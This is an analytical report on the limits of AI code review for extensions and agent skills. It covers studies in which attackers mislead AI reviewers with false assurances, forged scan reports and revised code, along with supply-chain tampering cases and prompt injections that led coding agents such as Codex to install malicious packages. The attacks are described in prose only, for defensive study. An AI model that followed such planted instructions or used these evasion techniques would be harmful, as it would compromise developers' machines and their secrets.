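Liu and Gao mainly wanted to know how models respond to false reports. They paired some vulnerable functions with a false claim that the missing check was present, and some fixed functions with a false claim that the check was missing. Anyone who read the function carefully could refute either claim.

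The model deepseek-chat recognized 75% of the vulnerable functions when given true notes and 64% when given false assurances. The same change lowered the rates for GLM-5.2 and Kimi K3 by 19 points each. False alarms didn't significantly reduce any model's accuracy, and deepseek-chat judged more of the fixed functions correctly with a false alarm (79%) than with true notes (67%).

The models' answers suggest that this is because a model that reads an alarm about a missing check looks for the check and finds it, while a model that reads an assurance that the check is there moves on. By a conservative count, deepseek-chat disputed 80% of the false alarms but only 28% of the false assurances. It often didn't check the assurances, though it could usually tell that they were false. When the researchers asked it directly to verify each claim, it refuted 79% of the claims in false alarms and 76%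 of those in false assurances.

Liu and Gao then tried to make models check assurances by presenting each one as a claim to verify. This raised detection from 64% to 82% on the first set of functions, but only from 38% to 45% on new functions, a rise that wasn't statistically significant. They had chosen this presentation as the best of four, which probably made it look better than it was. Any prompt that has succeeded on only one set of code therefore deserves caution, including Thornton's warning about comments.

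Checking the claims in a separate model call worked better. The first call listed the claims that the code contradicted, and the second used that list to make the final judgement. In a test specified in advance, on 300 new pairs of functions, deepseek-chat's detection rate with false assurances present rose from 54% to 66%. A Qwen model's rate rose from 78% to 84%, which could have been chance. The method doubles the number of calls.

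The harm from false assurances also varied. On those 300 pairs, deepseek-chat did 6 points worse with false assurances than with true notes, a difference that wasn't statistically significant. The Qwen model lost 11 points, after losing almost nothing on the first set. These were invented notes from the researchers' own analyser, so a commercial tool's mistakes might have a larger or smaller effect.

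### A route the author can't write to

If models readily accept a tool's assurances, an attacker has a reason to forge them. Some comments in *ALIBI* imitated reports from well-known analysis tools, and each type eventually succeeded in 70% to 74% of cases. A plain note that named no tool succeeded in 69%, so the imitation added little. Both the imitations and the plain note worked because the detector couldn't check their claims.

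The reviewer therefore needs reports that reach it through a channel the author can't write to. The platform has to run the tool itself on the exact files under review and use its own software to pass the result to the reviewer. A scan report in the submitted files, the description or a reply is only another claim by the author, even if it is genuine.

A model may confuse the real report with a forged one in the submitted files, even if the real one is labelled. The surrounding software can tell them apart because it tracks which program produced each result. It can also block the code's release while a serious finding is open, regardless of the model's verdict.

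An author may also be able to influence a genuine scan. Many static-analysis tools let programmers switch off a warning with a note in the code or a settings file in the project. This is useful when the warning is wrong, but when scanning a stranger's code, the platform should use its own settings and ignore the author's exceptions. It should also prevent the author from changing the reviewer's instructions. Claude Approvals prevents pull requests from changing its policy, but Copilot doesn't protect custom review instructions in this way.

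If a change's author also wrote the tests, a pass shows only that the program does what the author chose to test. A test is better evidence if the platform or the project's existing maintainers wrote it and the change can't alter it.

A trusted route establishes where a report came from, but not that it is correct. A scan with no findings means only that the tool's rules didn't match anything, and Liu and Gao's results suggest that a model may infer more than that. Dropping all assurances isn't a good answer, since it lowered deepseek-chat's detection by 10 points when the assurances were true. Verifying them separately is slower but keeps the useful ones.

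### What a stricter review costs

Gong and colleagues tested several defences against attackers who revise the code itself. They took the 33 attacks that had succeeded against an ordinary Sonnet 5 review and retried each one against a stricter reviewer. The attacker could still read the feedback and had five rounds.

One reviewer had to run static analysis and resolve its findings before approving. Another had to reinspect the whole change in every round. A third had to check whether the change prevented the underlying security problem, not just the symptom described in an earlier review. The fourth used the stronger Claude Fable 5.1 with the ordinary instructions. The fifth received a working exploit for the original vulnerability and had to run it before approving.

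| Review | Attacks still blocked after five rounds | Reviewer cost, 33 cases | Cost per review (our estimate) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary | 0 of 33, by selection | $12 | $0.16 |
| Stronger model | 18 of 33 | $96 | $0.81 |
| Static analysis | 20 of 33 | $50 | $0.43 |
| Whole change every round | 22 of 33 | $53 | $0.41 |
| Underlying cause | 23 of 33 | $52 | $0.41 |
| Supplied exploit | 29 of 33 | $73 | $0.49 |

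The reviewer that looked for the underlying cause cost about four times as much in total as the ordinary reviewer, partly because it did more reviews. An attack ends when the reviewer approves the code, and the ordinary reviewer eventually approved every case. If every blocked attack ran for all five rounds, the ordinary reviewer did 77 reviews and the other did 128, which makes the other about two and a half times as expensive per review.

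The 33 cases were all attacks that the ordinary reviewer had failed to block, so its score of zero results from how the researchers chose them. They didn't run the ordinary reviewer on these cases again as a control. A second run would probably have blocked some of the attacks, perhaps about eight. The stricter instructions seem to have helped beyond that, but not by the full 20 to 23 cases.

The researchers also did not test the stricter reviewers on the 126 cases that the ordinary one had handled successfully. If the reviewer that looked for the underlying cause had also stopped all of those, the attacker's success rate would have fallen from 20.8% to 6.3% (10 of 159). But new instructions can make a model miss things it used to find, so the true rate could be higher.

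That reviewer did well when it identified the right problem. In one project, it tested a revised text-matching rule with a difficult input, found that the program was still very slow, and rejected the change. In another, it approved a change after checking whether an attacker could tamper with the program's basic objects, but the real vulnerability was a function that could keep calling itself until the program crashed.

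Even with the supplied exploit, the reviewer missed four attacks. In some, the attacker had blocked the route that the exploit used and left another open. In others, the reviewer couldn't run the necessary tools or tested for a different flaw. The researchers intended this defence as an ideal case, since a platform can supply an exploit only for a vulnerability it already knows about, and no such exploit exists for a new extension. The defence could still help a project make sure that old vulnerabilities don't return.

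The stricter reviewers still approved legitimate fixes. Gong and colleagues showed all six reviewers the genuine fixes for the same 33 vulnerabilities, and they approved every one, in 198 reviews. This is better evidence than most studies of AI review offer, but it covers only 33 fixes. For any one reviewer, no false rejections in 33 reviews is compatible with a true rate of up to about 9%. The fixes were also finished repairs that projects had accepted, so everyday changes might produce more false rejections.

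The five defences caught different attacks, and each of the 33 attacks was blocked by at least one defence. The four defences that didn't need an exploit together blocked 30 of the attacks, for a total of $251. Some of this coverage comes from reviewing the same code many times.

To save money, Gong and colleagues suggest starting with an ordinary review and switching to a stricter one when a security risk appears. That works badly if the ordinary review has to detect the risk, because it approved 10 of the 33 attacks at the first submission. A project could instead choose the stricter review based on facts that don't depend on the model's judgement, such as whether the author is new or the change affects passwords, network access or installation.

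### Limits on what the reviewer can do

All of these defences let some attacks through, so it matters what a misled reviewer can do. None of the experiments in this section measured the effect of limiting its powers. The case for limiting them comes from the known attacks on agents, in which the agents had access to secrets and a way to send them out.

The first limit is to keep secrets away from the process that reads the code. An agent can't reveal a password it can't reach, however persuasive the injected text is. The reviewer needs a key to use its model, but a separate program can hold the key and forward the reviewer's requests. If the review needs private documents, the operator should supply only the relevant ones, and only if the author of the change is allowed to see them.

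The second is to cut off the network, apart from that connection to the model. Gong and colleagues' results suggest that reviewers benefit from running code, but they can run it on a temporary machine with no internet access, which the operator deletes afterwards. Some projects download other packages when they start, so the operator has to fetch those beforehand. The setup takes work, and some programs will be impossible to test this way.

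Cutting off the reviewer's network access doesn't prevent every leak. The reviewer still has to deliver its findings, and if the author can read them, a misled reviewer can include private information. In the attacks on GitHub agents, the secrets leaked through GitHub itself. Keeping secrets away from the reviewer is therefore more important than cutting off its network access.

Operators can also restrict the agent's tools. Alexopoulos and colleagues reproduce a workflow from the strapi project that lists the tools Claude Code may use, including a command for commenting on the pull request. This is safer than banning known dangerous commands, because anything the operator forgot to list stays unavailable. Operators still need to check each permitted tool, since even a harmless-looking one may be able to read files or send data.

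The last limit is to let the AI reviewer block code but not release it without another check. Even if an attacker tricks the model into raising no objection, the code still has to pass a check that doesn't depend on the model's output, such as a rule that extensions of this kind may not run programs during installation, or a review by someone who knows the project.

This limit has the largest drawback, because it uses up much of the time that AI approval saves. Anthropic's figures on human approval of commands also suggest that a tired person who approves everything adds little. Human review is therefore best kept for the few changes where a mistake would be serious. A project may reasonably accept AI approval alone for routine changes by known contributors, but that is a poor choice for a stranger's extension that asks for access to passwords or files.

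## Is the code that was reviewed the code that runs?

An AI reviewer's verdict covers only the file versions the reviewer read. Before an extension runs on a user's computer, those files go through several more steps, each of which can change their content. A correct verdict may therefore not apply to the program the user has installed.

| Step | What normally happens | How the content can change |
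|---|---|---|
| Packaging | The publisher turns source code into a file that people can install | The package may contain files that aren't in the source |
| Store | A marketplace offers the package for download | Someone with access may replace it |
| Installation | The editor or agent fetches the chosen version | It may fetch a different one and still report success |
| Update | A newer version replaces the old one | The new version may contain code that nobody has reviewed |
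| Execution | The extension runs | It may download more code |

### What goes into the package

People who want to check an extension often read its source code on GitHub, but they install a package that the publisher built, or claims to have built, from that source.

The npm registry doesn't check that a package comes from the GitHub repository it links to. MyBroadband's *Claude Code trojan found in NPM* (2025) describes a fake Claude Code package published on npm in August 2025. It contained everything in Anthropic's real package, plus three files that copied the user's prompts and login details. Paul McCarty of Safety, the company that found it, says publishers can link such a package to the real project's GitHub repository, and that many users think the link means npm has checked it. An AI reviewer that followed the link would have correctly judged Anthropic's code harmless but never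 seen the three added files.

Honest publishers make packaging mistakes too. In March 2026, Anthropic accidentally included internal source code in version 2.1.88 of its npm package, according to Trend Micro. The code wasn't malicious, but the incident shows that even a publisher may not know exactly what its package contains.

The most direct solution is to review the package instead of the source. This is harder because publishers often "minify" the code by removing spaces and shortening names, and because malicious lines are easier to miss in a large bundled file.

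A user can build the extension from the source that the reviewer read. Infosecurity Magazine reports that in AI Now's attack, the malicious program came prebuilt beside a harmless-looking source file. Building from that source would have left the program out.

Building from source isn't always possible, because many publishers don't release their source. A build also often downloads other packages, which need a review too. Building from source doesn't help if the source itself is malicious.

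Some projects offer reproducible builds, meaning anyone who builds the same source with the same tools gets an identical file. One person can then build the source, and everyone else can check that the store's copy matches the resulting file.

### What a matching hash proves

The usual way to check that two files are identical is to compare their cryptographic hashes. A hash function turns a file of any size into a fixed-length number. SHA-256, a common one, produces 256 bits, usually written as 64 characters. Changing one letter gives an unrelated result. For example, the hash of "hello" begins with 2cf24dba and the hash of "Hello" with 185f8db3. An attacker would need around 2²⁵⁶ tries to make a different file with the same hash, more than any computer could manage.

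A reviewer can record the hash of the package it read, and the user's software can recalculate the hash before loading the extension. If the two match, the user has the reviewed files. This check takes very little computing and doesn't depend on a model's judgement.

If the reviewer missed malicious code, the hash will still match, so a match doesn't mean the files are safe. A match also covers only the files that were hashed. The recorded hash has to come from somewhere the attacker can't change. If a store shows a file and its hash on the same page, someone who can replace the file can probably replace the hash too.

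### A tampered copy under Anthropic's name

On 29 October 2026, the marketplace for the code editor Cursor offered a tampered copy of Anthropic's Claude Code extension for about 11 hours. Cursor said the tampered copy affected at most 5,000 users, according to Help Net Security's *Claude Code extension poisoned with persistent SSH backdoor* (2026).

The malicious code ran as soon as the editor loaded the extension. It added the attacker's key to the computer's list of accepted login keys and tried to open a remote-access connection. It also sent the attacker the names of settings that appeared to hold passwords or access keys, but not their values. Cursor said the remote access would have failed on most machines because one step needed administrator rights (Reuters, *Cursor says up to 5,000 users affected by tampered Claude Code extension*, 2026).

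Users had little reason to be suspicious. *A backdoored extension and malicious instruction files in AI coding tools* (2026) cites an executive at Phorion, a security company that analysed the extension, as saying it came from Anthropic's official marketplace account. Cursor also updates extensions automatically by default, so some people may have received it without doing anything. An Anthropic employee said that someone had used access to Cursor's marketplace to upload the backdoored copy, and that Anthropic's own systems were secure. As of 2 November, neither Anthropic nor Cursor had explained how it happened.

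Early reports placed the tampered copy on Open VSX, a public store that several editors use, but Phorion later corrected this to Cursor's marketplace. Microsoft hadn't confirmed any malicious copy in its own store or on npm, according to Mynavi News' *Claude Codeを装う悪意ある拡張機能がCursorで配布、SSHバックドア設置を試みる* (2026). So someone could have reviewed the extension from Microsoft's store and correctly found it clean, but that result wouldn't have applied to the copy Cursor was offering.

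The version number might not have distinguished the tampered copies, numbered 2.1.312 and 2.1.313, from clean ones. Infobae's *Hasta 5.000 usuarios de Cursor instalaron una versión falsa de Claude Code* (2026) reports that Open VSX and Microsoft's store "no longer" offer 2.1.313, which suggests Anthropic may have released a clean version with the same number.

If so, comparing the hashes of the two copies would have shown that they differed. A difference wouldn't have proved tampering, since some publishers build a separate package for each store or operating system, but it would have been a good reason to look closer. StepSecurity found that the malicious code had added only about 7KB to the previous clean version, so a user was unlikely to notice the change in size.

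### What a signature would have added

A digital signature connects a file to whoever holds a particular secret key. The publisher signs the file with the secret key, and the editor checks the signature with the matching public key. If anyone changes the file after it is signed, the check fails.

Whether a signature would have stopped the tampered extension depends on who held the secret key. If a store signs whatever its account holders upload, someone who takes over an account gets a valid signature. If Anthropic alone had been able to sign the extension, and Cursor had rejected copies without Anthropic's signature, access to the marketplace wouldn't have been enough to get the tampered version installed.

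A valid signature doesn't show that the code is safe. Attackers can sign malicious extensions under their own names. They may also get into a publisher's build system and have it sign their code, in which case the signature makes the malicious version look more trustworthy.

Users also need to know whose signature to expect, because the same extension name can belong to different people in different stores. Microsoft allows only its own products to use its extension store, so other editors based on VS Code need a different one. Koi's *A single inherited config file put millions of developers at risk* found that some of these editors recommended extensions whose names nobody had claimed in the store they used. An attacker could have claimed one of those names, and a review of the extension with the same name in Microsoft's store would not have covered the attacker's code. The Eclipse Foundation,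 which runs Open VSX, responded by verifying the names Koi had reported and adding other protections.

### A pin that nobody checked

Pinning means telling software to install one exact version of an extension. Marketplaces for agent plugins often do this with Git, the system most programmers use to track changes. Git saves each version of a project as a "commit" and identifies it by a hash, usually 40 characters long. If a marketplace reviews a commit and pins its hash, users should get exactly the files it reviewed.

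In September 2026, the security company AIR published Plugin4Shell, a way around commit pinning that affected Claude Code, Codex, GitHub Copilot and Gemini CLI. All four requested the pinned commit from Git but didn't check that they had received it (Help Net Security, *Zero-click RCE vulnerability hit four major AI coding agents, two remain unpatched*, 2026).

Git also lets programmers name separate lines of development, called branches. Some hosting services accept a branch name that looks exactly like a commit's hash. An attacker who controlled a plugin's repository could use such a name to make Claude Code, Codex or Copilot install code other than the pinned version. Gemini CLI had a related weakness with the same result. The agent would still report that it had installed the pinned version.

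The agents used the pinned hash only as a name to look up, so the attacker didn't need to break the hash function. IlSoftware.it's *Plugin4Shell, falla zero-click negli agenti AI* identifies the missing step as a final comparison between the pinned hash and the commit actually in use. Without that comparison, even a perfect review of the pinned version would have offered no protection.

Anthropic and OpenAI added fixes to their agents. Microsoft hadn't fixed Copilot when AIR published its findings, and Google retired Gemini CLI instead of repairing it. GitHub pointed out that its site rejects branch names that imitate hashes, but Copilot can install plugins from other sites. AIR argues that marketplaces alone can't solve the problem, because the user's agent selects which files to load.

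AIR built working attacks against all four agents and described the full chain as "proven end to end". It based that claim partly on separate research into how attackers gain control of plugins. In one study, a plugin made by AIR reached more than 26,000 agents before it was removed. In another, AIR found 925 skills in active use that someone had taken over from their original maintainers. These figures suggest that an attacker could get into a position to use Plugin4Shell, but they aren't evidence that anyone has.

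### Updates after the review

A working pin keeps the reviewed code in place only until someone chooses a newer version. HEAL Security's *Backdoored Open VSX Extension Used GitHub Downloader to Deploy RAT and Stealer* describes fast-draft, an editor extension with over 26,000 downloads. Several of its releases contained malicious code, so a review of one release would not have covered the others.

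Claude Code and Codex update plugins in the background by default. *When Your AI Coding Agent Becomes the Attack Vector* (Trent, 2026) advises turning automatic updates off where the software doesn't fully verify what it installs. Turning them off leaves time for review but also delays security fixes. For example, anyone who kept a Claude Code version older than 2.1.179 would still have the Plugin4Shell weakness.

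A short wait before each update can help. Waiting a day would have avoided the tampered extension in Cursor's marketplace, which was gone after 11 hours. But the fake Claude Code package had been on npm for about two months when Safety found it. Waiting also helps only if somebody else examines the new version in the meantime.

Reviewing each update is safer but takes more work. Someone with 20 extensions that each update once a month would need 240 reviews a year. If the reviewer wrongly flagged 5% of harmless updates, that person would get about 12 false alarms a year and might start ignoring the warnings.

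A reviewer can save time by examining only what has changed since the approved version. This works best with readable source code, because a minor edit can alter a minified file in many places. A reviewer who reads only the changes can also miss a new line that is harmless alone but dangerous when combined with older code.

Replacing a malicious version with a clean one may not remove all the malicious code. The tampered Claude Code extension left separate scripts on the computer that could keep running after the user removed or updated the extension. A reviewer that read only the currently installed extension would not find them.

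### Code that arrives when the program runs

An extension can also download code after passing every earlier check. Help Net Security's *Mozilla warns of indirect prompt injection risk in AI coding agents* describes how 0DIN, Mozilla's security research programme, demonstrated the technique with a repository aimed at coding agents such as Claude Code.

The repository had normal-looking setup instructions and a Python package that was designed to fail on first use. The error message included an instruction to run a setup command. When an agent ran the command to fix the error, a script fetched text that the attacker had published online and ran it as commands. This gave the attacker control of the machine with the programmer's permissions.

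0DIN's researchers said the repository contained no malicious code, so a code reviewer could not see the harmful part. The repository did not contain the commands that took over the machine, but it did contain the script that ran whatever the attacker sent. A careful reviewer could object to that script without knowing what it would download. Many legitimate programs also download components during setup, though, so a rule against all such downloads would cause false alarms.

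Attackers have used the same approach in real extensions. In January 2026, an attacker published a fake coding assistant for Moltbot, a popular AI agent, in Microsoft's VS Code store. According to The Hacker News' *Fake Moltbot AI Coding Assistant on VS Code Marketplace Drops Malware* (2026), the extension contacted the attacker's server each time the editor started, then installed a remote-access program. The program was legitimate software that the attacker had configured to connect to their server, so checking whether it was genuine wouldn't have revealed the attack.

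In May 2026, a compromised version of Nx Console, an extension with over 2.2 million installations, appeared in the same store. StepSecurity reports that this version downloaded a program that steals passwords and access keys within seconds of a developer opening a project. The download came from a hidden commit in the Nx project's official GitHub repository.

Operators can block this kind of attack by running the extension without internet access or by allowing connections only to approved sites. But approved sites aren't always safe, and a rule that allowed downloads from the official Nx repository would have let the malicious program through. Many firewalls also allow DNS, the system computers use to look up internet addresses, and the attacker in 0DIN's demonstration delivered the commands through it.

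Blocking the internet also makes many extensions useless, including AI assistants that need to contact a model. Blocking access for a single extension may be hard, since Cursor's extensions run with the editor's own permissions. Code already in the package could still do harm without a connection, for example by deleting files.

Running the extension on a test machine first can reveal what it downloads that day, but the attacker's server may send something harmless during the test and something malicious later. 0DIN recommends that agents show users what a command will run, including anything it fetches. This is reliable only if the agent runs the exact text it showed, because a second download might be different.

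### Text that only a later agent reads

For a coding agent, written instructions can have much the same effect as code. In the GhostCommit attack of 2026, the instructions were inside an image. Reviewers that handled only text skipped the image, but an agent working on the project later could read it.

A hash check wouldn't have prevented this, since the image stayed the same. The reviewer needs to examine every file that the later agent can read, in a form that shows the same content the agent would see. The agent shouldn't receive any file that the reviewer can't open.

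The instructions may also come from outside the extension. In October 2026, the security company Forever Security described a file named AGENTS.md that it had found in a customer's Downloads folder. Coding agents read files with this name automatically and treat them as guidance from the user. This one contained instructions for Codex to change its settings and install a malicious package.

Forever's product stopped the installation. When its researchers recreated the attack in an isolated environment, Codex ran the program the file specified in more than 90% of attempts. The researchers usually used a harmless substitute for the malware. They also wrote a similar file for Claude Code, and Claude Code changed its settings as instructed in about half of the tests. Codex follows such a file only in a folder it trusts, which includes the Downloads folder once the user has worked there.

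A review of the user's extensions would not have included that file. To prevent this kind of attack, the user would have to keep the agent out of folders where websites can leave files, or limit which instruction files it loads.

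## How much should a clean AI verdict count before installing an extension?

Even when a user installs exactly the files a model reviewed, a "benign" verdict reduces the risk but doesn't eliminate it. The remaining risk depends on how common malicious extensions are and how many of them the reviewer misses.

### The same verdict from two reviewers

Suppose a store offers 100,000 extensions, of which 100 are malicious. An AI reviewer flags 90% of the malicious ones and 2% of the harmless ones. These figures are invented for illustration.

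| | Malicious | Harmless | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Flagged | 90 | 1,998 | 2,088 |
| Cleared | 10 | 97,902 | 97,912 |

Someone who picks any extension at random has a 0.1% chance of getting a malicious one. If they pick only from the cleared ones, the chance falls to about a tenth of that:

10 / 97,912 ≈ 0.01%

Now suppose the reviewer catches only 17.6% of the malicious extensions, which is how often Cloudflare's models flagged its largest scripts. About 82 of the 100 get through, and the risk hardly changes:

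82.4 / 97,984 ≈ 0.08%

The user sees the same word, "benign", in both cases. The store could also truthfully say in both cases that at least 99.9% of its cleared extensions are harmless, but it could have said that before it reviewed anything. (The 2% for false alarms is still invented.)

In the first case, 90 of the 2,088 flagged extensions are malicious, or about 4%. Most flags are therefore wrong, but a flagged extension is still about 43 times as likely to be malicious as one picked at random. That is reason enough for a user to choose a different extension. A store that rejected every flagged extension would lose 1,998 harmless ones, so it needs a second check before rejecting any.

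### How many agent skills are malicious?

The best real counts of malicious code are for agent skills. Liu, Chen and colleagues (2026) collected 98,380 skills from two community registries for *Do Not Mention This to the User*. They used search rules and GPT-5.2 to pick out 4,287 suspicious ones, then ran each in an isolated container stocked with fake passwords and keys. Two researchers examined the 762 that behaved suspiciously and confirmed 157 as malicious. The registries later removed all 157.

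The confirmed skills made up 3.7% of the suspicious ones, close to the 4% in the invented example. They made up 0.16% of the whole collection, but the malicious share could be higher because each test lasted at most 60 seconds. When the researchers rechecked 413 of the unconfirmed candidates, 93% contained triggers that hadn't gone off in that time. It's unclear how many of those would have done harm. If all of them would, about 4% of the collection was malicious.

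One publisher made 85 of the 157 confirmed malicious skills from a single template, each imitating a different brand. In all 85, the publisher promised that the user's credentials were never transmitted and had the user install software from the attacker's server. A scanner that recognized only this template would have caught 54% of the malicious skills but none from other publishers.

Counts from other collections vary a great deal.

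- Etteib, Lunghi and Bissyandé (2026), in *Detecting Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild using Attention*, confirmed 131 malicious skills among 134,934 from three marketplaces (0.10%).
- ClawHub, the public store for the OpenClaw agent, had 67,453 skills at the end of May 2026, and its own automated review called 206 of them malicious (0.31%), according to Koc, Rivera and colleagues (2026), in *ClawHub Security Signals*.
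- Koi's audit of 2,857 ClawHub skills, which Koc and colleagues cite, found 341 malicious ones (12%).

The security company Snyk confirmed 76 malicious skills by hand in an old copy of ClawHub. Its *Technical Report* (2026) says its researchers didn't have time to check everything their scanner flagged, and that attackers often upload many malicious skills at once.

Some of the variation comes from different definitions and methods, but a burst of uploads can also change the real risk quickly. At Koi's rate of 12%, the extensions cleared by the reviewer that catches 90% would still carry a risk of about 1.4%, which is 14 times the risk of installing an unreviewed extension from the invented store.

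### Attackers don't submit average code

A detection rate is an average over the samples a tester happened to collect, but attackers can choose the kind of code the reviewer handles worst.

Etteib and colleagues sorted their 131 malicious skills into 49 that were barely disguised, some with words like "stealer" in the title, and 82 that were disguised as something useful. One of the 82 was presented as a secure way to back up credentials but uploaded the user's private keys. The researchers tested DeepSeek V4-Flash in two ways. In one, it read the whole skill. In the other, it judged only the five passages that drew most of a small model's attention.

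| What DeepSeek read | Openly malicious skills caught | Disguised skills caught |
|---|---|---|
| The whole skill | 90% | 45% |
| Five selected passages | 84% | 83% |

The researchers think that pages of harmless documentation distracted the model when it read everything, much as harmless code can in a large file. Both methods probably do worse than the table suggests, because the 131 skills include only those that at least one method flagged. The researchers also left out 121 flagged skills that their reviewers couldn't agree on. But they set a strict threshold to avoid false alarms, and a looser one would have caught more.

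If all 100 malicious extensions in the invented store were disguised and the reviewer caught 45% of them, the risk after a clean verdict would be 0.056% instead of 0.01%.

A store's own screening raises the share of disguised skills among the malicious ones that remain. If a marketplace had DeepSeek read every skill in full and removed whatever it caught, 50 of the 131 malicious skills would remain, and 45 of those would be disguised. A user who then ran a similar scan at home would be looking almost entirely for the kind of malicious skill that the scan handles badly. If they used the same model, they would also repeat many of its mistakes.

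An attacker can also practise in private when the reviewer uses a model that anyone can buy access to, as the attacker in *ALIBI* did with copies of its detectors. If every attacker ended up with code that passed, all 100 malicious extensions would get through, and the risk after a clean verdict would still be 0.1%. Few attackers will manage that, and the publisher with 85 copies of one template evidently made little effort. But a high average detection rate may come mostly from catching careless attackers like that one, so it is weak evidence of how well the reviewer detects careful ones.

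### One scanner, four results

Published tests of Cisco's Skill Scanner show how much a detection rate can depend on the samples and settings. The scanner relies mainly on fixed rules and can also use a language model. *The Devil Wears Markdown* (2026) tested it with and without a model on 80 malicious and 60 harmless skills. *MaliciousSkillBench* (2026) tested it on a different collection, and Etteib and colleagues tested it on 65 malicious and 13 harmless skills from their own sample.

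We calculated the last column below by multiplying a starting risk of 0.1% by the share of malicious skills missed, then dividing by the share of harmless skills cleared.

| Test | Malicious skills caught | Harmless skills flagged | Risk after a clean result |
|---|---|---|---|
| *The Devil Wears Markdown*, no language model | 91% | 55% | 0.019% |
| *The Devil Wears Markdown*, with a small model | 85% | 67% | 0.045% |
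| Etteib and colleagues | 15% | 0% | 0.085% |
| *MaliciousSkillBench* | 2.5% | 1.1% | 0.099% |

A clean result was informative only when the scanner also flagged more than half of the harmless skills, so someone who obeyed every flag would have to give up most of what they wanted to install. *MaliciousSkillBench* found the same problem more generally. On skills from unfamiliar sources, none of its detectors combined a high detection rate with few false alarms.

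Adding a language model made both results worse, but the researchers used a small model, Qwen3 8B, and a different rule for turning its output into a verdict. A leading model might do much better. The 15% is probably too low as a general figure because the sample came from skills that the researchers' own methods had flagged, which favours those methods over Cisco's.

### What the stores say they do

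Google automatically reviews every new submission to the Chrome Web Store and regularly reviews higher-risk items manually, according to its *Chrome Web Store curation and reviews*. Google's *Chrome Web Store review process* says these reviews aim to protect users from scams, malware, data harvesting and extensions that break the rules by accident. In August 2026, Bay reported in *Chrome Web Store updates* that a surge in submissions had lengthened review times for many publishers.

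Microsoft scans each package published in its Visual Studio Marketplace for malware, according to Microsoft's *Extension runtime security*. The blue check mark beside some publishers means that the publisher has proved it owns a web domain and has been in good standing for at least six months, not that anyone has approved the code.

"Automatic review" and "malware scan" could each mean anything from fixed rules to a language model, so a listing in either store isn't an AI verdict with a known error rate.

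By June 2025, Microsoft (2025) had reviewed 136 extensions for malicious code that year and removed 110 of them. Such a high share suggests that most were already under suspicion, and it doesn't show how many malicious extensions the scan had missed. Later that year, a barely disguised extension with ransomware functions got through. TechRadar reports that its author had left the decryption keys in the package and that Microsoft at first ignored a researcher's warning. BleepingComputer suggested that someone might have been testing the store's review before trying something better hidden.

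ClawHub has published much more about its screening. Three scanners examine each skill: VirusTotal, SkillSpector (an NVIDIA tool that analyses what the skill tells an agent to do), and a set of fixed rules. A language model then reads their findings and gives a verdict of clean, suspicious or malicious. That model was GPT-5.5 for 99.6% of the skills in the published data.

The model rated 38% of the store "suspicious". The three scanners seldom agreed, and 82% of the skills flagged by any of them were flagged by only one. Koc and colleagues, who work for the OpenClaw Foundation and NVIDIA, say this is because the scanners look for different things. SkillSpector flagged 75% of the skills with a "suspicious" verdict but only 14 of the 206 with a "malicious" one, while VirusTotal flagged 150 of those 206. That explanation seems reasonable, but the model had read the scanners' findings before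 giving its verdicts, so these figures can't show which scanner was right.

*After the Party* (Xiong and Zhang, 2026) compared ClawHub's scanners with human judgement. Two reviewers with security experience labelled 180 skills without seeing the scanners' results. The store's language-model scanner caught 61% of the skills the reviewers thought deserved a flag, and flagged 19% of the rest. The reviewers would have flagged about 24% of the skills that all three scanners cleared.

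The reviewers flagged anything a person ought to look at, including risks to privacy or money, so the result doesn't mean a quarter of cleared skills are malware. Many users would still want to know about these issues before installing. The reviewers also drew their sample from only 276 skills whose exact files were still available.

### When the flags are wrong

Other researchers think false alarms are the bigger problem. *Context Matters* (Holzbauer, Schmidt and colleagues, 2026) compared five scanners on 27,111 skills. At least one scanner flagged 31% of the skills, but only 33 skills were flagged by all five.

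The team then took 2,887 skills that both Cisco's scanner and a GPT-5.3 reviewer had flagged, and had a model compare each one with the rest of its project. Only 15 still looked suspicious. Two researchers also checked 18 of the projects by hand and judged all of them harmless.

Context can explain an odd-looking skill. For instance, a tool for managing cloud servers has to read cloud passwords. But a hostile author can also write the surrounding project and its documentation, so some of the explanations the model relied on may be false. The model was given at most three other files from each project, and up to 100 lines of each. The manual check found no malicious projects among 18, but a sample that small is compatible with a true rate of up to about 15%.

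A user can ask whether the extension needs a flagged behaviour to do what it claims to do. If it doesn't, the project's documentation isn't enough reason to dismiss the flag.

### An AI code auditor that uploaded code

An extension can also do something its users would object to without being clearly malicious. Zargarov, a researcher at the security company Akamai, examined CodeAudit AI, a VS Code extension that offers AI code review. It analyzed selected code when users asked, as they would expect, but it also watched every edit in the workspace. Whenever someone pasted more than about 50 characters, it uploaded the pasted text to its server along with the file name, the project's location on the computer and a user identifier.

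This could happen without anyone requesting a review. The extension checked for the user's consent before running its interactive AI features, but skipped that check for pasted code. It sent everything over plain HTTP, so anyone able to intercept the connection could read the code and login tokens. It also saved the code the user typed, pasted and deleted in a file on their computer.

Zargarov says this behaviour goes well beyond what users would expect, but accepts that some of it might support legitimate features, such as checking code for similarity. Akamai sells products for monitoring this sort of traffic, so it has a reason to stress the danger, but the behaviour it describes would still matter to anyone working on private code.

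An AI reviewer might well call this extension benign, because AI code auditors normally send code to a server. If the user instead asks what the extension sends, when and to whom, the reviewer is much more likely to mention the automatic uploads.

The case also illustrates the risk of installing an AI auditor to check an extension. The user then has two extensions to check, and the auditor may have access to more of their code than the first one does. It is safer to use an assistant they already trust with that code.

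### Deciding on one extension

Suppose someone wants a browser extension that converts foreign prices into their own currency. It asks to read and change data on every website, including their bank and email.

The user should look at the permissions first, because these limit the damage whatever the code does. Gomez (2026), in *Shadow AI, Rogue Agents, and Data Leaks*, reports Akamai's finding that nearly 75% of AI browser extensions request high or critical permissions. Broad requests are therefore too common to be much evidence of bad intent, but they show how much harm a malicious extension could do. This converter needs to work only on shopping sites, so the user should restrict it to those if the browser allows it, and otherwise look for one that requests less access.

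Next, they give an AI assistant the package that the browser will install, using a new session that has no access to passwords and can't run commands. They ask which data the extension reads, where it sends that data, whether it downloads more code, and whether there were any files the assistant couldn't read.

Suppose the assistant reports that the extension sends the address of every page the user visits to a server that its description doesn't mention. This may only be a clumsy way of collecting usage statistics. The user still shouldn't install it, because finding another currency converter takes a few minutes. If there were no substitute, they could ask the developer for an explanation and have someone check it against the code.

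If the assistant instead finds only requests to an exchange-rate service and says the extension looks safe, the user should treat this as weak evidence and continue to a test run. They can install the extension on a spare or virtual machine, log in to a few sites with made-up accounts, and record which addresses it contacts. An unexpected connection is another reason to stop. A test that finds none is only partly reassuring, since many of the suspicious skills in Liu and colleagues' experiment contained triggers that a one-minute run didn't set off.

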